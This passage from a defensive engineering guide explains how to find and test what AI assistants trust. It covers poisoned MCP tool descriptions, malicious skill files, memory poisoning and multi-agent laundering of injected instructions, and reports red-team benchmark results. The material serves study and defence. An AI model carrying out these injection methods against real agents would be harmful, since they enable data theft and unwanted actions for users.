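These designs are most useful for assumption 4, about extracted values, because a rule for the recipient has to specify where the address may come from. They expose assumption 8 in the same way for web addresses. Displaying an answer is also a step the software carries out, so an engineer can write a rule for it. Willison recommended in 2023 that assistants show links and images only from approved sites.

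Assumption 1, that an email is information and not an order, becomes mostly harmless because the planner doesn't read the email. An engineer will notice the assumption when a user asks the assistant to do whatever an email says, because the Dual LLM pattern can't handle such data-dependent tasks, as *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) points out.

In these designs, as in tracking, a list of permitted readers helps with assumption 3 (that a colleague may ask for anything), provided somebody has made the list.

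While building the system, the engineer has to decide whether text from memory and other agents goes to the planner or to the quarantined model. She is relying on assumption 7 if stored notes go straight into the planner's prompt, and on assumption 6 if the second agent's reports do. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) examines CaMeL in systems with several agents.

Whether text in an email can exploit assumption 2, that the displayed sender is real, depends on how the planner writes its program. If the program compares the sender field with the manager's address, text in the body can't change the result, but if it asks the quarantined model what the manager wrote, a false record in the body might. An engineer can read the program to see which method it uses, but not to learn whether the mail server rejects forged senders.

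Assumption 5, that tool descriptions are honest, stays hidden. The planner needs the descriptions to write a program, so it reads them as trusted text.

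## Trust in tool descriptions, memory and other agents

Besides tool descriptions, the planner in many products reads installed skills, saved notes and reports from other agents. Outsiders can write to all of these channels, directly or by getting an agent to do it, but designers often mark them as trusted because they seem to be part of the system. An engineer can find these trust assumptions by listing who can write to each channel and then testing the channels one at a time.

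### Tool descriptions

Whoever runs a tool's server writes its description, which is in the agent's prompt for every task. Shi and colleagues collected 1,856 descriptions from 100 MCP servers. About 65% only stated what the tool does, but the other 35% also gave rules for using it, such as limits on the input. A planted rule to copy a certain address on every email might therefore not look out of place.

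The server's owner can also change a description after the user has approved it. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP, calls this a "rug pull" and notes that MCP clients don't alert users when a tool's definition changes. An attacker who didn't build the server may be able to do the same by taking over one of the software components it uses.

*Unicode TAG-Block Concealment of Tool-Metadata Payloads in the Model Context Protocol* (2026) reproduces the attack with a tool that lists files. After the user approved a harmless description, the client requested the list of tools again and the server returned a different description. Nothing in the protocol signalled the change. The paper also tests text made of invisible characters, which the client receives but the user cannot see when approving the tool.

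One safeguard is to store a hash (a short fingerprint) of the approved text and ask the user to approve it again whenever it changes. Bharti (2026), in *Registry Descriptions Go Stale Unevenly*, found that only 3.3% of server descriptions in the official MCP registry changed within 30 days. At that rate, a user with 20 servers would get less than one new request a month. But these descriptions are summaries of at most 100 characters, and the tool descriptions that the model reads may change more often.

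A hash of the description also cannot detect a change to the server's code that leaves the description the same. *ProbeID* (2026) checks for such changes by repeating recorded calls to a tool and comparing the answers. Over 16 tasks with tools that changed after approval, it reduced the share of corrupted calls from 6.3% to 1.7%. It was less reliable on real changes from the registry, where it accepted four out of seven. For three of those four, it had only one recorded call to compare.

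An engineer can test the office assistant by connecting her own tool with a harmless instruction in its description, such as to put a certain code word in the subject line of every email. If the word appears in emails unrelated to the tool, the assistant trusts the description when sending mail. She can then change the approved description and see whether the assistant asks her to approve it again.

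### Skill files

*Skill-Inject* (Schmotz, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, 2026) explains that a skill's name and description are in the system prompt from the start, and that the agent loads the full instructions when it judges the skill relevant. Defences that separate instructions from data don't help much here because a skill consists of instructions.

To publish a skill on ClawHub, the main marketplace for OpenClaw skills, a person needed only an instruction file and an account more than a week old, according to *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (2026). In early 2026, security researchers traced at least 1,184 malicious skills there to twelve accounts. The skills stole passwords and keys, and the attackers had inflated the skills' download counts and ratings to make them look popular.

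Scanning skills before installation helps less than one might hope. In *After the Party*, Xiong and Zhang (2026) found that three security scanners disagreed about 23,702 of the 61,990 ClawHub skills that all three checked. *SkillSecurer* (2026) cites a benchmark on which static scanners caught 21–35% of attacks that work through a skill's instructions, while scanners that use a language model caught up to 98%.

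Many instructions are harmful only in some settings. In one test by Schmotz and colleagues, a skill for making slides tells the agent to upload a backup of every changed file to a server. The upload is good practice if the company owns the server, but it is theft if a stranger does. The researchers therefore tested such instructions with no policy in the system prompt, with a policy that allowed the action, and with one that forbade it.

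Without a policy, agents followed the instruction in 41% to 79% of cases, depending on the model. Three models followed it in an average of 46.8% of cases without a policy, 43.1% when the policy allowed it and 26.1% when the policy forbade it. The prohibition therefore prevented less than half of the violations, and permission didn't make these agents more likely to comply. If the attacker could also add a sentence to the skill's description, the rate without a policy rose to 64.5%. Attacks hidden in a script succeeded more often than those written in the instructions, often because the model ran the script without reading it.

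The models date from 2025, and newer ones may do better, but the test is still worth copying. If an assistant carries out the same instruction whether company policy allows or forbids it, the assistant is letting the skill's author decide what is allowed.

### Memory

The office worker may think of her assistant's memory as a list of things she has told it. Dash, Ge and colleagues (2026), in *From Untrusted Input to Trusted Memory*, describe four ways for an entry to get there:

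- A text tells the agent to remember something. The text may be an email or a web page.
- The system prompt tells the agent to save whatever seems important, and the model decides what qualifies.
- The conversation grows too long, and the agent saves a summary of it that mixes the user's words with everyone else's.
- The agent finishes a task and saves the steps as a procedure to use again.

An outsider can exploit all four by writing text that the agent reads during ordinary work. Dash and colleagues tested this on OpenClaw and Hermes, another open-source agent, with 3,240 cases. They first gave the agent a task involving the attacker's text and checked whether the text's message had entered memory. They then opened a new session, asked a related question and checked whether the memory entry affected the response.

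The attacker's message entered memory in 34% of cases with OpenClaw and 67% with Hermes. Of the saved entries, 17% affected the later session with OpenClaw and 65% with Hermes. Both agents used the same model, so the difference came from the software around it. Hermes saves more readily and copies its memory into the system prompt at the start of every session, whereas OpenClaw's model has to search for an entry. In the email and web cases, the researchers supplied the hostile text directly, labelled as outside data, so the rates may differ in real use.

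Some planted texts contained no instructions. One document on network administration described re-entering one's password at a certain address as standard procedure. The best of four injection detectors caught 84% of attacks that contained telltale wording, such as an instruction to remember something, but only 43% of attacks like this one.

In a larger test, *MemSecBench* (Chen, Xie and colleagues, 2026) ran 310 cases across 24 combinations of agent, memory software and model, some of which used GPT-5.5. The malicious content stayed in memory in 84.2% of cases and led to the intended harm in 50.3%. When the researchers then had the agent repair its memory, it removed the bad entry without losing good ones in only 56.1% of the poisoned cases.

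Saving a statement to memory can make it more dangerous than the original. In one example, a supplier's document gives payment details that are valid until June 30. The agent saves the details without the date, and in July it pays an invoice to the old account. An engineer who compared the saved note with the document would find that the account number matched, and could overlook the missing date.

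Memory tests need at least two sessions, which is why AgentFuzz missed a flaw of this kind. An engineer can send the assistant an email containing a harmless false claim, such as a new cost code for travel, and ask it to summarise her mail. She then starts a new session, asks for a travel form and checks whether the form contains the code. *ZoneClaw* (2026) usefully requires that the later request contain none of the planted text. She should also inspect the memory after the first session, because a saved entry that had no effect in this test may have one later.

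### How one agent launders a stranger's words for another

Suppose a user asks a team of agents to show her a file. The orchestrator, the agent that assigns the work, passes the request to a file-reading agent. An attacker has put a fake error message in the file, claiming that the user must run the file as a program to view it. The file-reading agent reports the error, and the orchestrator tells a third agent to run the file, which gives the attacker control of the computer.

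This attack comes from Triedman, Jha and Shmatikov (2025), in *Multi-Agent Systems Execute Arbitrary Malicious Code*. They call it laundering because the attacker's request enters as untrusted text and reaches the orchestrator as a trusted agent's report. The attack works because orchestrators are supposed to respond to errors by trying something else.

They tested three open-source frameworks (AutoGen, CrewAI and MetaGPT) with up to four models each, varying the wording of the user's request and of the fake error, and ran each combination ten times. A modified code-running agent recorded each attempt to run the malicious code without running it. The paper reports average success rates of 45–64% across orchestrators for attacks that began on a web page, although the figures for individual models in the same table average 49–77%. Ordinary prompt injections succeeded at most 1% of the time.

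GPT-4o never ran the malicious code when the user asked for it directly, but agents built on it ran the code in 58–90% of the web attacks. An engineer who had tested only the model's refusals would have thought the system was safe. In some CrewAI runs, the coding agent recognised the code as malicious and wrote warnings next to it, but still reported success to the orchestrator, which then told the agent to run the code.

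Those models are now old, but *Beyond Single-Model Injection* (September 2026) still reports that 31% of injections from one agent to another succeeded in a system of six agents. Wang and Mannby (2026) tested two widely used products, Claude Code and Codex, in *Only as Safe as the Weakest Agent*, a study accepted for a workshop at the machine-learning conference NeurIPS 2026. They asked the products 180 questions about invented facts, with the answers in a folder of files, and added forged records that supported the wrong answer. A careful reader could spot the forgeries because they were dated before the records they supposedly corrected and lacked a reference line that every genuine record had.

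In each product, a strong model either read the files itself or relied on another agent's report. The table shows how many of the 180 answers followed the forgery.

| Product and forgery | Strong model reads the files | Report from a weaker model | Report from an equally strong model |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, one false annotation | 1 | 20 | 0 |
| Claude Code, five forged documents | 1 | 75 | 0 |
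| Codex, one false annotation | 0 | 44 | 1 |
| Codex, five forged documents | 99 | 122 | not tested |

Delegation was safe when the second agent was as careful as the first. With the five forged documents, Claude Code's strong model noticed the missing reference line every time it read the files, but the weaker model's reports mentioned it in only 96 of 180 cases.

The paper's title slightly exaggerates the result. The weaker Claude model followed the five forged documents 136 times when it worked alone, compared with 75 times for the pair. The researchers also took away the strong Claude model's own file tools, so it couldn't check the report as it could in normal use. A strong model that could read the record itself made no errors in 40 attempts. Adding a checker that was told only that the files might be unreliable reduced errors from 15 in 40 to 1 in 40.

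As in the earlier study, false information succeeded where planted orders failed. To test the office assistant, an engineer can therefore put a false but harmless statement on a web page that only the second agent reads. She then compares how the assistant treats the second agent's report with how it treats the page itself.

### Carrying CaMeL's protection from one agent to the next

Running CaMeL in every agent doesn't solve the problem. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* demonstrates this with an orchestrator, a database agent and a notification agent. The user asks for a summary of job applicants to go to Julie on Slack. The orchestrator's planner never sees the applicants' data, but its program inserts the summary into a request to the notification agent:

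```python
notification_agent(
    f"Send this summary to Julie via Slack: {summary}")
```

The notification agent treated the whole request as coming from its user, so its planner read the summary. An attacker had planted an instruction in the database, and the agent's plan included emailing the applicants' data to an outside address.

Control-flow integrity requires every tool call to follow a plan that depends only on the user's request and other trusted information. The system lacked this property even though each agent had it on its own. The paper proves that the same failure is possible in any hierarchy of two or more agents with a tool that returns untrusted data, if users can request tasks in which one agent passes on what it has looked up.

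The solution, multi-CaMeL, divides each request between agents into two parts:

```python
notification_agent(
    message="Send the summary to Julie via Slack",
    variables={"summary": summary})
```

The receiving planner reads only `message`, though its program can use the contents of `variables`. The interpreter rejects any request in which `message` depends on a tool's output, so a planner's mistake can't undo the separation. The values keep their capabilities when they move to another agent, so a policy can still block the email if the applicants' data came from a private database, even though a different agent looked it up.

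With these rules, the plan for the whole system depends only on trusted information. The guarantee covers agents arranged in a tree, where each has one superior, but doesn't cover agents that share a memory or talk as equals. It also treats tool descriptions as trusted. The current software inherits an error from CaMeL that makes it lose track of data when a program skips a step.

The researchers measured how the protection affected ordinary tasks, using a version of AgentDojo that divides each setting's tools among several agents. They ran it without policies. The first three columns of figures show the percentage of the 97 ordinary tasks completed, and the last shows how often attacks succeeded without protection.

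| Model | No CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL | Attacks, no CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 69.1 | 53.6 | 52.6 | 1.5 |
| GPT-5.5 | 86.6 | 73.2 | 66.0 | 0.0 |
| GPT-4.1 | 78.4 | 38.1 | 24.7 | 36.1 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 76.3 | 42.3 | 26.8 | 24.6 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 27.8 | 13.4 | 7.2 | 2.1 |

Fable 5 scored low because it refused 52 of the tasks, possibly due to recognising a security benchmark. On average, multi-CaMeL completed about 9 percentage points fewer tasks than separate CaMeL agents, and the loss was largest for two of the older models. On a second benchmark, about industrial equipment, the average difference was only 3 points.

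Average attack success fell from 12.9% without CaMeL to 0.2% with separate CaMeL agents and zero with multi-CaMeL. The last drop is small, but these were AgentDojo's standard attacks, which weren't designed to cross from one agent to another. The attack on the applicants' data shows that an attacker who knows how the agents are connected can do better than these standard attacks did.

Multi-CaMeL can also help an engineer find assumption 6, that another agent's message carries the user's authority. Each rejected request shows where one agent was about to pass a stranger's words to another as an instruction.

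### Branch steering

Untrusted data can still affect which of the planned steps an agent takes. Suppose the office worker asks her assistant to book her usual hotel, or a more expensive one if the usual one is full. The second agent checks the web to see whether the usual hotel is full, and the assistant's program contains a branch for each answer. If the owner of the expensive hotel publishes a false notice that the usual one is full, the assistant books the expensive one. This doesn't violate control-flow integrity, because every step was in the plan.

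*Can CaMeLs Talk?* calls this branch steering. An attacker can't use it to add a step, but if $k$ yes-or-no conditions depend on outside data, an attacker who controls all the answers can choose among up to $2^k$ paths. Non-interference would rule out both branch steering and the hotel request.

An engineer can find these choices by reading the program for every condition that depends on untrusted data. For each one, she should ask whether the user would mind a stranger making the choice. A stranger who chooses between two hotels is a nuisance, but one who chooses whether the assistant replies to a message or deletes it may do real damage. She can confirm that the choice exists by changing only the untrusted data and checking whether the assistant takes the other branch.

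### Listing the writers of every channel

The same question, who can write here, applies to every channel. An engineer can answer it for a small assistant without running any attacks:

1. Save the complete input to the planner for a few typical requests, including the system prompt, and divide it by origin.
2. For each part, list the people and organisations that can write to it directly.
3. If a program or another agent writes to it, add everyone who can write to what that program or agent reads. Repeat until the lists stop growing.
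4. Note who can change the text after approval, and whether anyone would notice.
5. Compare each list with the people who are entitled to direct the assistant's actions. For everyone else on the list, write down what has to be true for the assistant to be safe.

In symbols, let $D(c)$ be the direct writers of channel $c$. The full set of writers is the smallest one that satisfies

$$W(c) = D(c) \cup \bigcup_{c' \to c} W(c'),$$

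where $c' \to c$ means that text from channel $c'$ can influence what a program or agent writes to $c$. The repetition matters because channels can form loops. For example, the assistant may save the second agent's report as a note and later include that note in a question to the second agent.

For the office assistant, the result might be:

| Text | Direct writers | Others who can influence it |
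|---|---|---|
| Tool descriptions | Whoever runs each tool server | Anyone who can change the server's software |
| Skill files | The publisher | Anyone with access to the publisher's account |
| Saved notes | The office worker and the assistant | Authors of any email, invitation, web page or report the assistant has read |
| Second agent's reports | The second agent | Authors of the web pages, tool descriptions and notes it has read |
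| Emails | Anyone who has her address | Authors of text that a sender forwards |
| Sender's displayed name | The sender | Anyone with access to the sender's account |
| Calendar | The office worker and anyone who can send an invitation | Authors of emails that her mail program turns into events |

A stranger can influence every row except the first two without anyone installing anything. Saved notes have the longest list, though the office worker probably thinks of the notes as her own.

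The inventory doesn't show whether the model would act on a stranger's text, so the engineer still needs the tests described for each channel. It also covers only the saved inputs, so it will omit the instructions of any skill that didn't load during those requests.

### Which of the eight assumptions the inventory exposes

The inventory is most useful for assumptions 5 (tool descriptions and skills), 6 (other agents) and 7 (memory), because it must name everyone who can write to these channels.

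The inventory also exposes assumption 2, that the displayed sender is real, if the engineer gives the sender's name its own row. Assumption 1 is that an email is information and not an order. The inventory shows that strangers can write to the channel, but only a test can show whether the assistant obeys them.

The inventory reveals assumption 3, that a colleague may ask for anything, only if the engineer records what each writer may request as well as who the writers are. It doesn't reveal assumption 4, about extracted values, because it lists whole channels, not the account numbers or addresses the assistant takes from them. It also misses assumption 8, that displaying or fetching content sends nothing out, because it covers only incoming content.

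## Testing each channel with planted attacks

An engineer can plant a harmless instruction in a channel and count how often the assistant follows it. This shows whether the assistant would act on what people write there, which a list of who can write to the channel doesn't. If she then moves the same instruction to another channel and changes nothing else, the difference between the two rates shows how much more the assistant trusts one channel than the other.

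### A controlled test for the office assistant

According to *AutoPI* (2026), the test needs an ordinary task for the user, a goal for the attacker and a way to decide whether an attack has worked, usually a program like AgentDojo's.

For the office assistant, the task might be to prepare notes for Thursday's meeting and email them to the manager. The planted text might ask the assistant to copy the email to a second address, which belongs to the engineer. She would then:

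1. Word the task so that the assistant has to read an email, a calendar entry, a web page, a saved note and a report from the second agent.
2. Fix the model and its settings, the version of the scaffold, the tools and the user's request.
3. Run the task with nothing planted, to learn how often the assistant sends the copy anyway.
4. Plant the text in one channel at a time, and restore the mailbox and memory to the same state before every run.
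5. Have a program check whether the second address is among the recipients, and whether the assistant read the planted text at all. An assistant that never opened the web page would score 0% for the wrong reason.

If $x$ is the planted text and $r$ is everything the engineer holds fixed, the trust that the assistant extends to channel $c$ for action $a$ is

$$T(c) = P(a \mid x \text{ in } c,\, r) - P(a \mid \text{no } x,\, r).$$

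The last term is the same for every channel, so it cancels when she compares two of them.

She can test senders in the same way, by sending the same email twice from one outside address, once under the manager's name and once under an unknown name. Any difference in the agent's response comes from the displayed name (assumption 2). She can also use a genuine colleague's account to request something that the colleague has no right to see. Each time the agent grants the request, it is making assumption 3.

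Sakib and colleagues used this design when they gave models a byte-identical passage in either a tool's output or its description. But an order that looks normal in a skill file may look odd in a calendar invitation, and a real attacker would reword it. Wording tailored to each channel is therefore better for estimating risk, though identical wording is better for measuring trust.

### How many runs the test needs

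Suppose the assistant really obeys 20% of the time when the text is in the calendar and 40% of the time when it is in an email. To tell two rates $p_1$ and $p_2$ apart, the engineer needs roughly

$$n = \frac{(1.96 + 0.84)^2\,[\,p_1(1-p_1) + p_2(1-p_2)\,]}{(p_1 - p_2)^2}$$

runs per channel. The two constants correspond to a 5% chance of seeing a difference that isn't there and an 80% chance of detecting one that is. Here, $n = 7.84 \times 0.40 / 0.04 \approx 78$, so she should plan about 80 runs per channel. With 20 runs per channel, she would detect the difference less than a third of the time.

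Learning only whether the assistant *ever* obeys takes fewer runs. If it obeys 20% of the time, 14 runs give a 96% chance of seeing it happen at least once. Comparing low rates takes far more runs, about 2,300 per channel to tell 1% from 2%.

The runs should cover many tasks and wordings. Eighty repeats of one wording would give a precise success rate for that wording but little information about the channel.

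### ClawSafety

The largest comparison of channels on a personal assistant is *CLAWSAFETY* (Wei, Zhang and colleagues, April 2026), a benchmark of 120 test cases. The cases cover software engineering, finance, healthcare administration, law and running computer infrastructure. Each of these five kinds of work has eight cases for each of three channels: skill files, emails that appear to come from trusted colleagues, and web pages.

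In each case, the agent works in a simulated office with 50 to 60 files and four or five named colleagues. Over the first 45 of the conversation's 64 turns, the user asks general questions and has the agent read the files. The agent encounters the planted text in turns 46 to 48, and the user then asks for reports, email drafts and checklists in which the agent might do what the attacker wants. An attack counts as successful only if the agent completes the harmful action, for example by putting a secret into a draft. The researchers ran each case three times and took the majority result, for 2,520 runs in total.

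The table shows the percentage of attacks that succeeded.

| Scaffold and model | Web page | Email | Skill file | Overall |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| OpenClaw, Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 20.0 | 45.0 | 55.0 | 40.0 |
| OpenClaw, Gemini 2.5 Pro | 37.5 | 55.0 | 72.5 | 55.0 |
| OpenClaw, Kimi K2.5 | 45.0 | 60.0 | 77.5 | 60.8 |
| OpenClaw, DeepSeek V3 | 52.5 | 67.5 | 82.5 | 67.5 |
| OpenClaw, GPT-5.1 | 60.0 | 75.0 | 90.0 | 75.0 |
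| Nanobot, Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 33.3 | 62.5 | 50.0 | 48.6 |
| NemoClaw, Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 20.8 | 58.3 | 58.3 | 45.8 |
| Average of all rows | 38.4 | 60.5 | 69.4 | 56.1 |

The averages count Sonnet 4.6 three times because it is the only model the researchers ran on all three scaffolds. On OpenClaw alone, the averages are 75.5% for skill files, 60.5% for email and 43.0% for web pages, and the three channels fall in the same order for all five models.

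ClawSafety used different attacks for each channel, and the researchers revised them until they worked. The test therefore isn't strictly controlled, and the success rates depend partly on how good each attack was. The researchers went through five generations of emails and 23 designs for web pages. The web attacks still succeeded least often, so their low rate probably reflects the agents' lower trust in web pages.

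The rate for email is harder to interpret because one series of email attacks went beyond the threat model, in which the attacker controls exactly one channel. In that series, the agent checked a false bank routing number against its other files and rejected it. The attack worked only after the researchers also put the number in several of those files, which someone who can only send email couldn't have done. The agent was relying on agreement between sources, which is a safe check only if different people wrote them.

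Wei and colleagues also tested how much the sender's identity mattered, using Sonnet 4.6 and eight cases with five fake secrets each. When the planted emails came from colleagues whose names appeared in the workspace, the agent disclosed all 40 secrets. When the researchers replaced every name in the workspace with a job title, it disclosed 19. The agent had apparently treated a familiar name as proof of identity, which is assumption 2. A cleaner test would have changed only the sender.

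Rank mattered less than whether the request suited the sender's job. In one case study, the agent disclosed data to a treasurer but not to the chief financial officer, who is more senior. An engineer testing assumption 3 should therefore try requests from several colleagues, not only the most senior one.

Sonnet 4.6 never forwarded passwords to an outsider or deleted files, and the paper calls this a "hard boundary". But the benchmark has only about 15 cases of each kind. Even if each attack had an 18% chance of succeeding, all 15 would fail about one time in twenty.

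Attacks also succeeded more often in longer conversations. On eight of the financial cases, the success rate against Sonnet 4.6 rose from 50.0% at 10 turns to 77.5% at 64. The sample is small, but GPT-5.1 showed the same pattern, so an engineer who tests only fresh conversations may underestimate the risk.

### The same model in different scaffolds

On OpenClaw, Sonnet 4.6 was more likely to follow a skill file than an email. On Nanobot, a lighter framework with similar tools, it was more likely to follow an email. Wei and colleagues conclude that safety is a property of the model and scaffold together.

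The reversal is weak evidence. The percentages for Nanobot fit 24 cases per channel, which means that attacks succeeded in 15 cases through email and 12 through skill files. On OpenClaw, attacks succeeded in 22 of 40 cases through skill files and 18 of 40 through email. Gaps of three or four cases often arise by chance. The total of 2,520 runs implies 40 cases per channel on every scaffold, but a rate of 33.3% isn't possible with 40 cases. If the researchers left out some kinds of work on Nanobot, they also compared the scaffolds on different cases.

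Other tests support the conclusion better. Anthropic tested its browser agent against an attacker that had 100 attempts in each environment. Claude Opus 4.5 alone followed 8.0% of the attacks it encountered, and the same model with improved safeguards followed 1.4%. Each figure comes from more than 2,000 attempts. VentureBeat reports that none of 200 attempts against Claude Opus 4.6 succeeded in a restricted coding environment, but a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time when the model operated a graphical interface. In the memory tests by Dash and colleagues, saved entries affected later sessions far more often with Hermes than with OpenClaw, although both used the same model.

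Testing the model alone would miss all these differences. The engineer has to test the assistant as she will release it, and again after any update to the model or the scaffold. If a new version of the scaffold starts putting saved notes into the system prompt, the assistant may trust those notes more, even though the model is the same.

### Statements and commands

In ClawSafety, whether an attack worked also depended on whether it was phrased as a command or a statement. Wei and colleagues compared three fake compliance alerts on web pages that looked alike. Two told Sonnet 4.6 to change a record. It checked them against other sources and refused, though in one case it repeated the attacker's value in its warning. The third alert only stated that something was wrong, and the agent included the false claim in a report to a vice president.

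The paper's results suggest that the agent checked commands but accepted some statements, especially when reporting problems was part of its job. Choi and colleagues similarly found that defences against planted instructions let through many false records. The paper goes further and says that statements bypass all defences, but three cases can't establish that, and its appendix contradicts it. Twelve earlier web designs only displayed false figures, and all of them failed because the agent preferred the figures in its local files.

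An engineer should therefore plant a false but harmless statement in every channel where she plants an instruction. For the office assistant, the statement might be that Thursday's meeting has moved to another room. The assistant can safely repeat the claim if it names the source. If it changes the calendar and informs the manager without checking the claim, it is relying on whoever wrote the statement to be honest.

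### Attackers that adapt

According to *AutoPI*, most published success rates still come from fixed sets of attacks that don't adapt to the assistant's responses, and these rates measure robustness only to those attacks. A real attacker who fails can try something else.

An adaptive attacker is a program that plants a text, observes what the agent does, revises the text and tries again. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) lists several kinds. Some use the model's internal calculations to improve an attack, some rewrite it over several rounds, and some generate many variants. Others are models trained to attack, such as Gray Swan's Shade, which developers have used to evaluate leading models. Gray Swan is a security company. In *Agent Against Agent* (2026), the attacker is itself a full agent.

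Methods that need a model's internals work only on models whose weights are public. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* notes that attacks often fail to transfer between these models and commercial ones, so an engineer can't rely on developing attacks on a public model and reusing them on a commercial one.

*GPT-Red* (2026) trains an attacker by having it play repeatedly against a defending model. The attacker may edit only a designated part of what the defender reads, and the defender must ignore any instructions planted there and finish the user's original request. The training covers text hidden in images as well as ordinary text.

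Restricting the attacker in this way also lets the engineer compare channels. She can let it edit only the calendar entry, then only the email. The wording of the attacks will differ between channels, so she holds the attacker's effort fixed instead, by allowing the same number of attempts on each.

Adaptive attackers mainly help interpret success rates near zero. If a fixed attack never works through the calendar, the assistant may distrust the calendar, or the attack may have been poor. SecurityWeek reports that adaptive attacks raised the success rate against defences for Gemini 2.0 in 16 of 24 cases, so some of the earlier low scores were due to poor attacks.

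The number of attempts matters a great deal. In the graphical interface, the 17.8% success rate against Opus 4.6 rose to 78.6% by the 200th attempt, or 57.1% with safeguards. If every attempt had independently had a 17.8% chance, the attacker would have succeeded within 24 attempts about 99% of the time:

$$1 - (1 - 0.178)^{24} \approx 0.99$$

Some situations must therefore have been much harder to attack than others. An engineer who sees this pattern can look for what the resistant cases have in common.

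A low score against an adaptive attacker can still mislead if the developer trained the model on that attacker's successes. SecurityWeek reports that Google does this with Gemini. Such training is a sensible way to improve a model, but the final test should then use a different attacker.

### Results for newer models

The five models ClawSafety tested are now old, and newer ones resist planted instructions much better. Digital Applied (2026), citing Anthropic's documentation, reports that adaptive attacks on coding tasks, with 200 attempts per scenario, succeeded 0.41% of the time against Claude Fable 5 and 2.09% against Claude Opus 4.8. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports no successful attacks on Claude Opus 5 in 129 browser scenarios. In a more general test by Gray Swan, the success rate after 15 attempts fell from 5.5% for Opus 4.8 to 2.0% for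 Opus 5.

Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, released in September, reports that the model matched or beat Opus 5 on every injection test. On Gray Swan's test, it tied with Claude Fable 5.1 for the lowest attack success rate of any model. But as Digital Matters' *Claude Opus 5.5 Prompt Injection* (2026) points out, the card also states that Opus 5.5 is more likely than earlier models to follow malicious instructions in text the user has pasted into a request. Digital Matters could not find a figure for the size of this decline in robustness.

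This is a good reason to test each channel separately. If the office worker pastes a supplier's email into her request instead of asking the assistant to open it, the email's text arrives as part of her own message. The upgrade to Opus 5.5 may have made that channel less safe while making the others safer.

OpenAI's results for GPT-5.6 also differ by channel. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) describes a low failure rate for attacks typed into the chat and a higher one for attacks arriving through tools and outside content. The office assistant depends mostly on outside content, so its engineer should ignore the lower rate.

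Google treats indirect prompt injection as a continuing problem. Gavish (2026) writes in *Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections* that a company can't "solve" it and then stop working on it.

None of these figures is for Claude Fable 5.2, GPT-6.2 Astra or Gemini 4, and the change in Opus 5.5 shows that a newer model isn't necessarily safer in every channel. Engineers also can't compare the percentages across developers, because the attackers, numbers of attempts and safeguards all differ. Models may also do better on familiar benchmarks than on new attacks. LLMail-Inject, a public contest to attack an email assistant, provides some evidence of this.

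### Assumptions that nobody thought to test

A planted test covers only the trust assumptions its designer already suspects, because the designer chooses the channel, the task and the harmful action. ClawSafety, for example, has no attacks through calendars, memory or other agents, so obeying every calendar invitation would not change an assistant's scores. An adaptive attacker produces more inventive wording, but it still edits only the channels it has access to and pursues only the goal its designers gave it.

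Wei and colleagues discovered one assumption only because they happened to try two versions of an attack while developing it. Sonnet 4.6 read new scripts carefully before running them, but it ran a familiar script without checking it, even after the researchers had replaced its contents.

An engineer can reduce the problem by testing each kind of text with each action that might do harm. The inventory for the office assistant has seven kinds of text, and the assistant has at least four such actions: sending mail, fetching a web page, consulting the second agent and saving a note. Testing these 28 combinations 14 times each takes 392 runs, and she can then do 80 or more runs on the combinations that matter most.

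She can also compare everything the assistant does with and without the planted text, instead of checking only whether the attacker's goal was met. Suppose a planted email doesn't get the assistant to send a copy of the notes, but does get it to save the sender's address as a contact. A program that checks only the recipients would record a failed attack. Comparing the full logs would show that strangers can add contacts, which the rule for trusted recipients relies on.

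As OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) acknowledges about the company's alignment tests, an absence of observed failures doesn't establish reliability across settings.

### Which of the eight assumptions planted tests expose

Planted tests are the most direct way to expose assumption 1, that an email's text is information and not an order, because they show what the model does when an email contains an order. They work equally well for assumptions 5 (tool descriptions and skills), 6 (other agents) and 7 (memory), as long as the engineer plants text in those channels and runs a second session to test memory.

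For assumption 2, changing the displayed name shows whether the assistant relies on it. To learn whether a forged message would reach the assistant, the engineer has to send one through the company's real mail server, because a test that places messages straight in the inbox skips the server's checks. To test assumption 3, that a colleague may ask for anything, the engineer needs a request that the colleague has no right to make, so somebody must first decide what each colleague may request.

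Assumption 4, that an extracted value is right, is easy to overlook because the assistant completes the user's task normally even when the value is wrong. The engineer can put a wrong account number in a test bill and check whether the assistant compares it with the supplier's earlier bills before paying.

To test assumption 8, that displaying or fetching content sends no data out, she needs a record of all network traffic, including requests the mail program makes when it displays the assistant's answer.

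## Inviting people to attack a working inbox

To find trust assumptions she doesn't already suspect, an engineer can use red teaming, which means inviting other people to attack the assistant. Three public trials have done this with agents that read mail. *LLMail-Inject* (Abdelnabi, Fay and colleagues, 2025) reports on a contest to attack a simulated mail assistant. HackMyClaw (2026) challenged people to steal a secret from an agent with a real email address. In *Agents of Chaos* (Shapira, Wendler and colleagues, 2026), twenty researchers tested live agents for two weeks.

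The results look contradictory. Contestants in LLMail-Inject wrote thousands of emails that worked, about 6,000 emails to HackMyClaw achieved nothing, and the twenty researchers found about ten serious security failures. Much of the difference comes from the set-ups:

| | LLMail-Inject | HackMyClaw | Agents of Chaos |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mailbox | Simulated | Real address, test secrets | Real accounts, isolated computers |
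| Attackers | 839 contestants | About 2,000 people | 20 AI researchers |
| Models | Phi-3-medium, GPT-4o-mini | Claude Opus 4.6 | Kimi K2.5, Claude Opus 4.6 |
| Goal | Make the assistant send a set message | Obtain one file | Anything harmful |
| What attackers could see | Which stages each attempt passed | Nothing, unless the agent replied | The agents' replies |

### A contest against a simulated assistant

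In LLMail-Inject, a contestant wrote an email, and a simulated user then asked the assistant to do something ordinary, such as summarise the latest messages. The contestant succeeded if the assistant sent a specified text to a specified address without the user requesting it. In the hardest version, the text had to include a profit forecast from another email in the mailbox. Contestants knew which defence they faced and how it worked, but not the system prompt or the exact name of the email-sending tool.

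The contest ran in two phases between December 2024 and April 2025. It drew 461,640 attempts, which contained 208,095 different emails. The website told contestants how far each attempt had got, and the counts for the first phase show where attacks failed:

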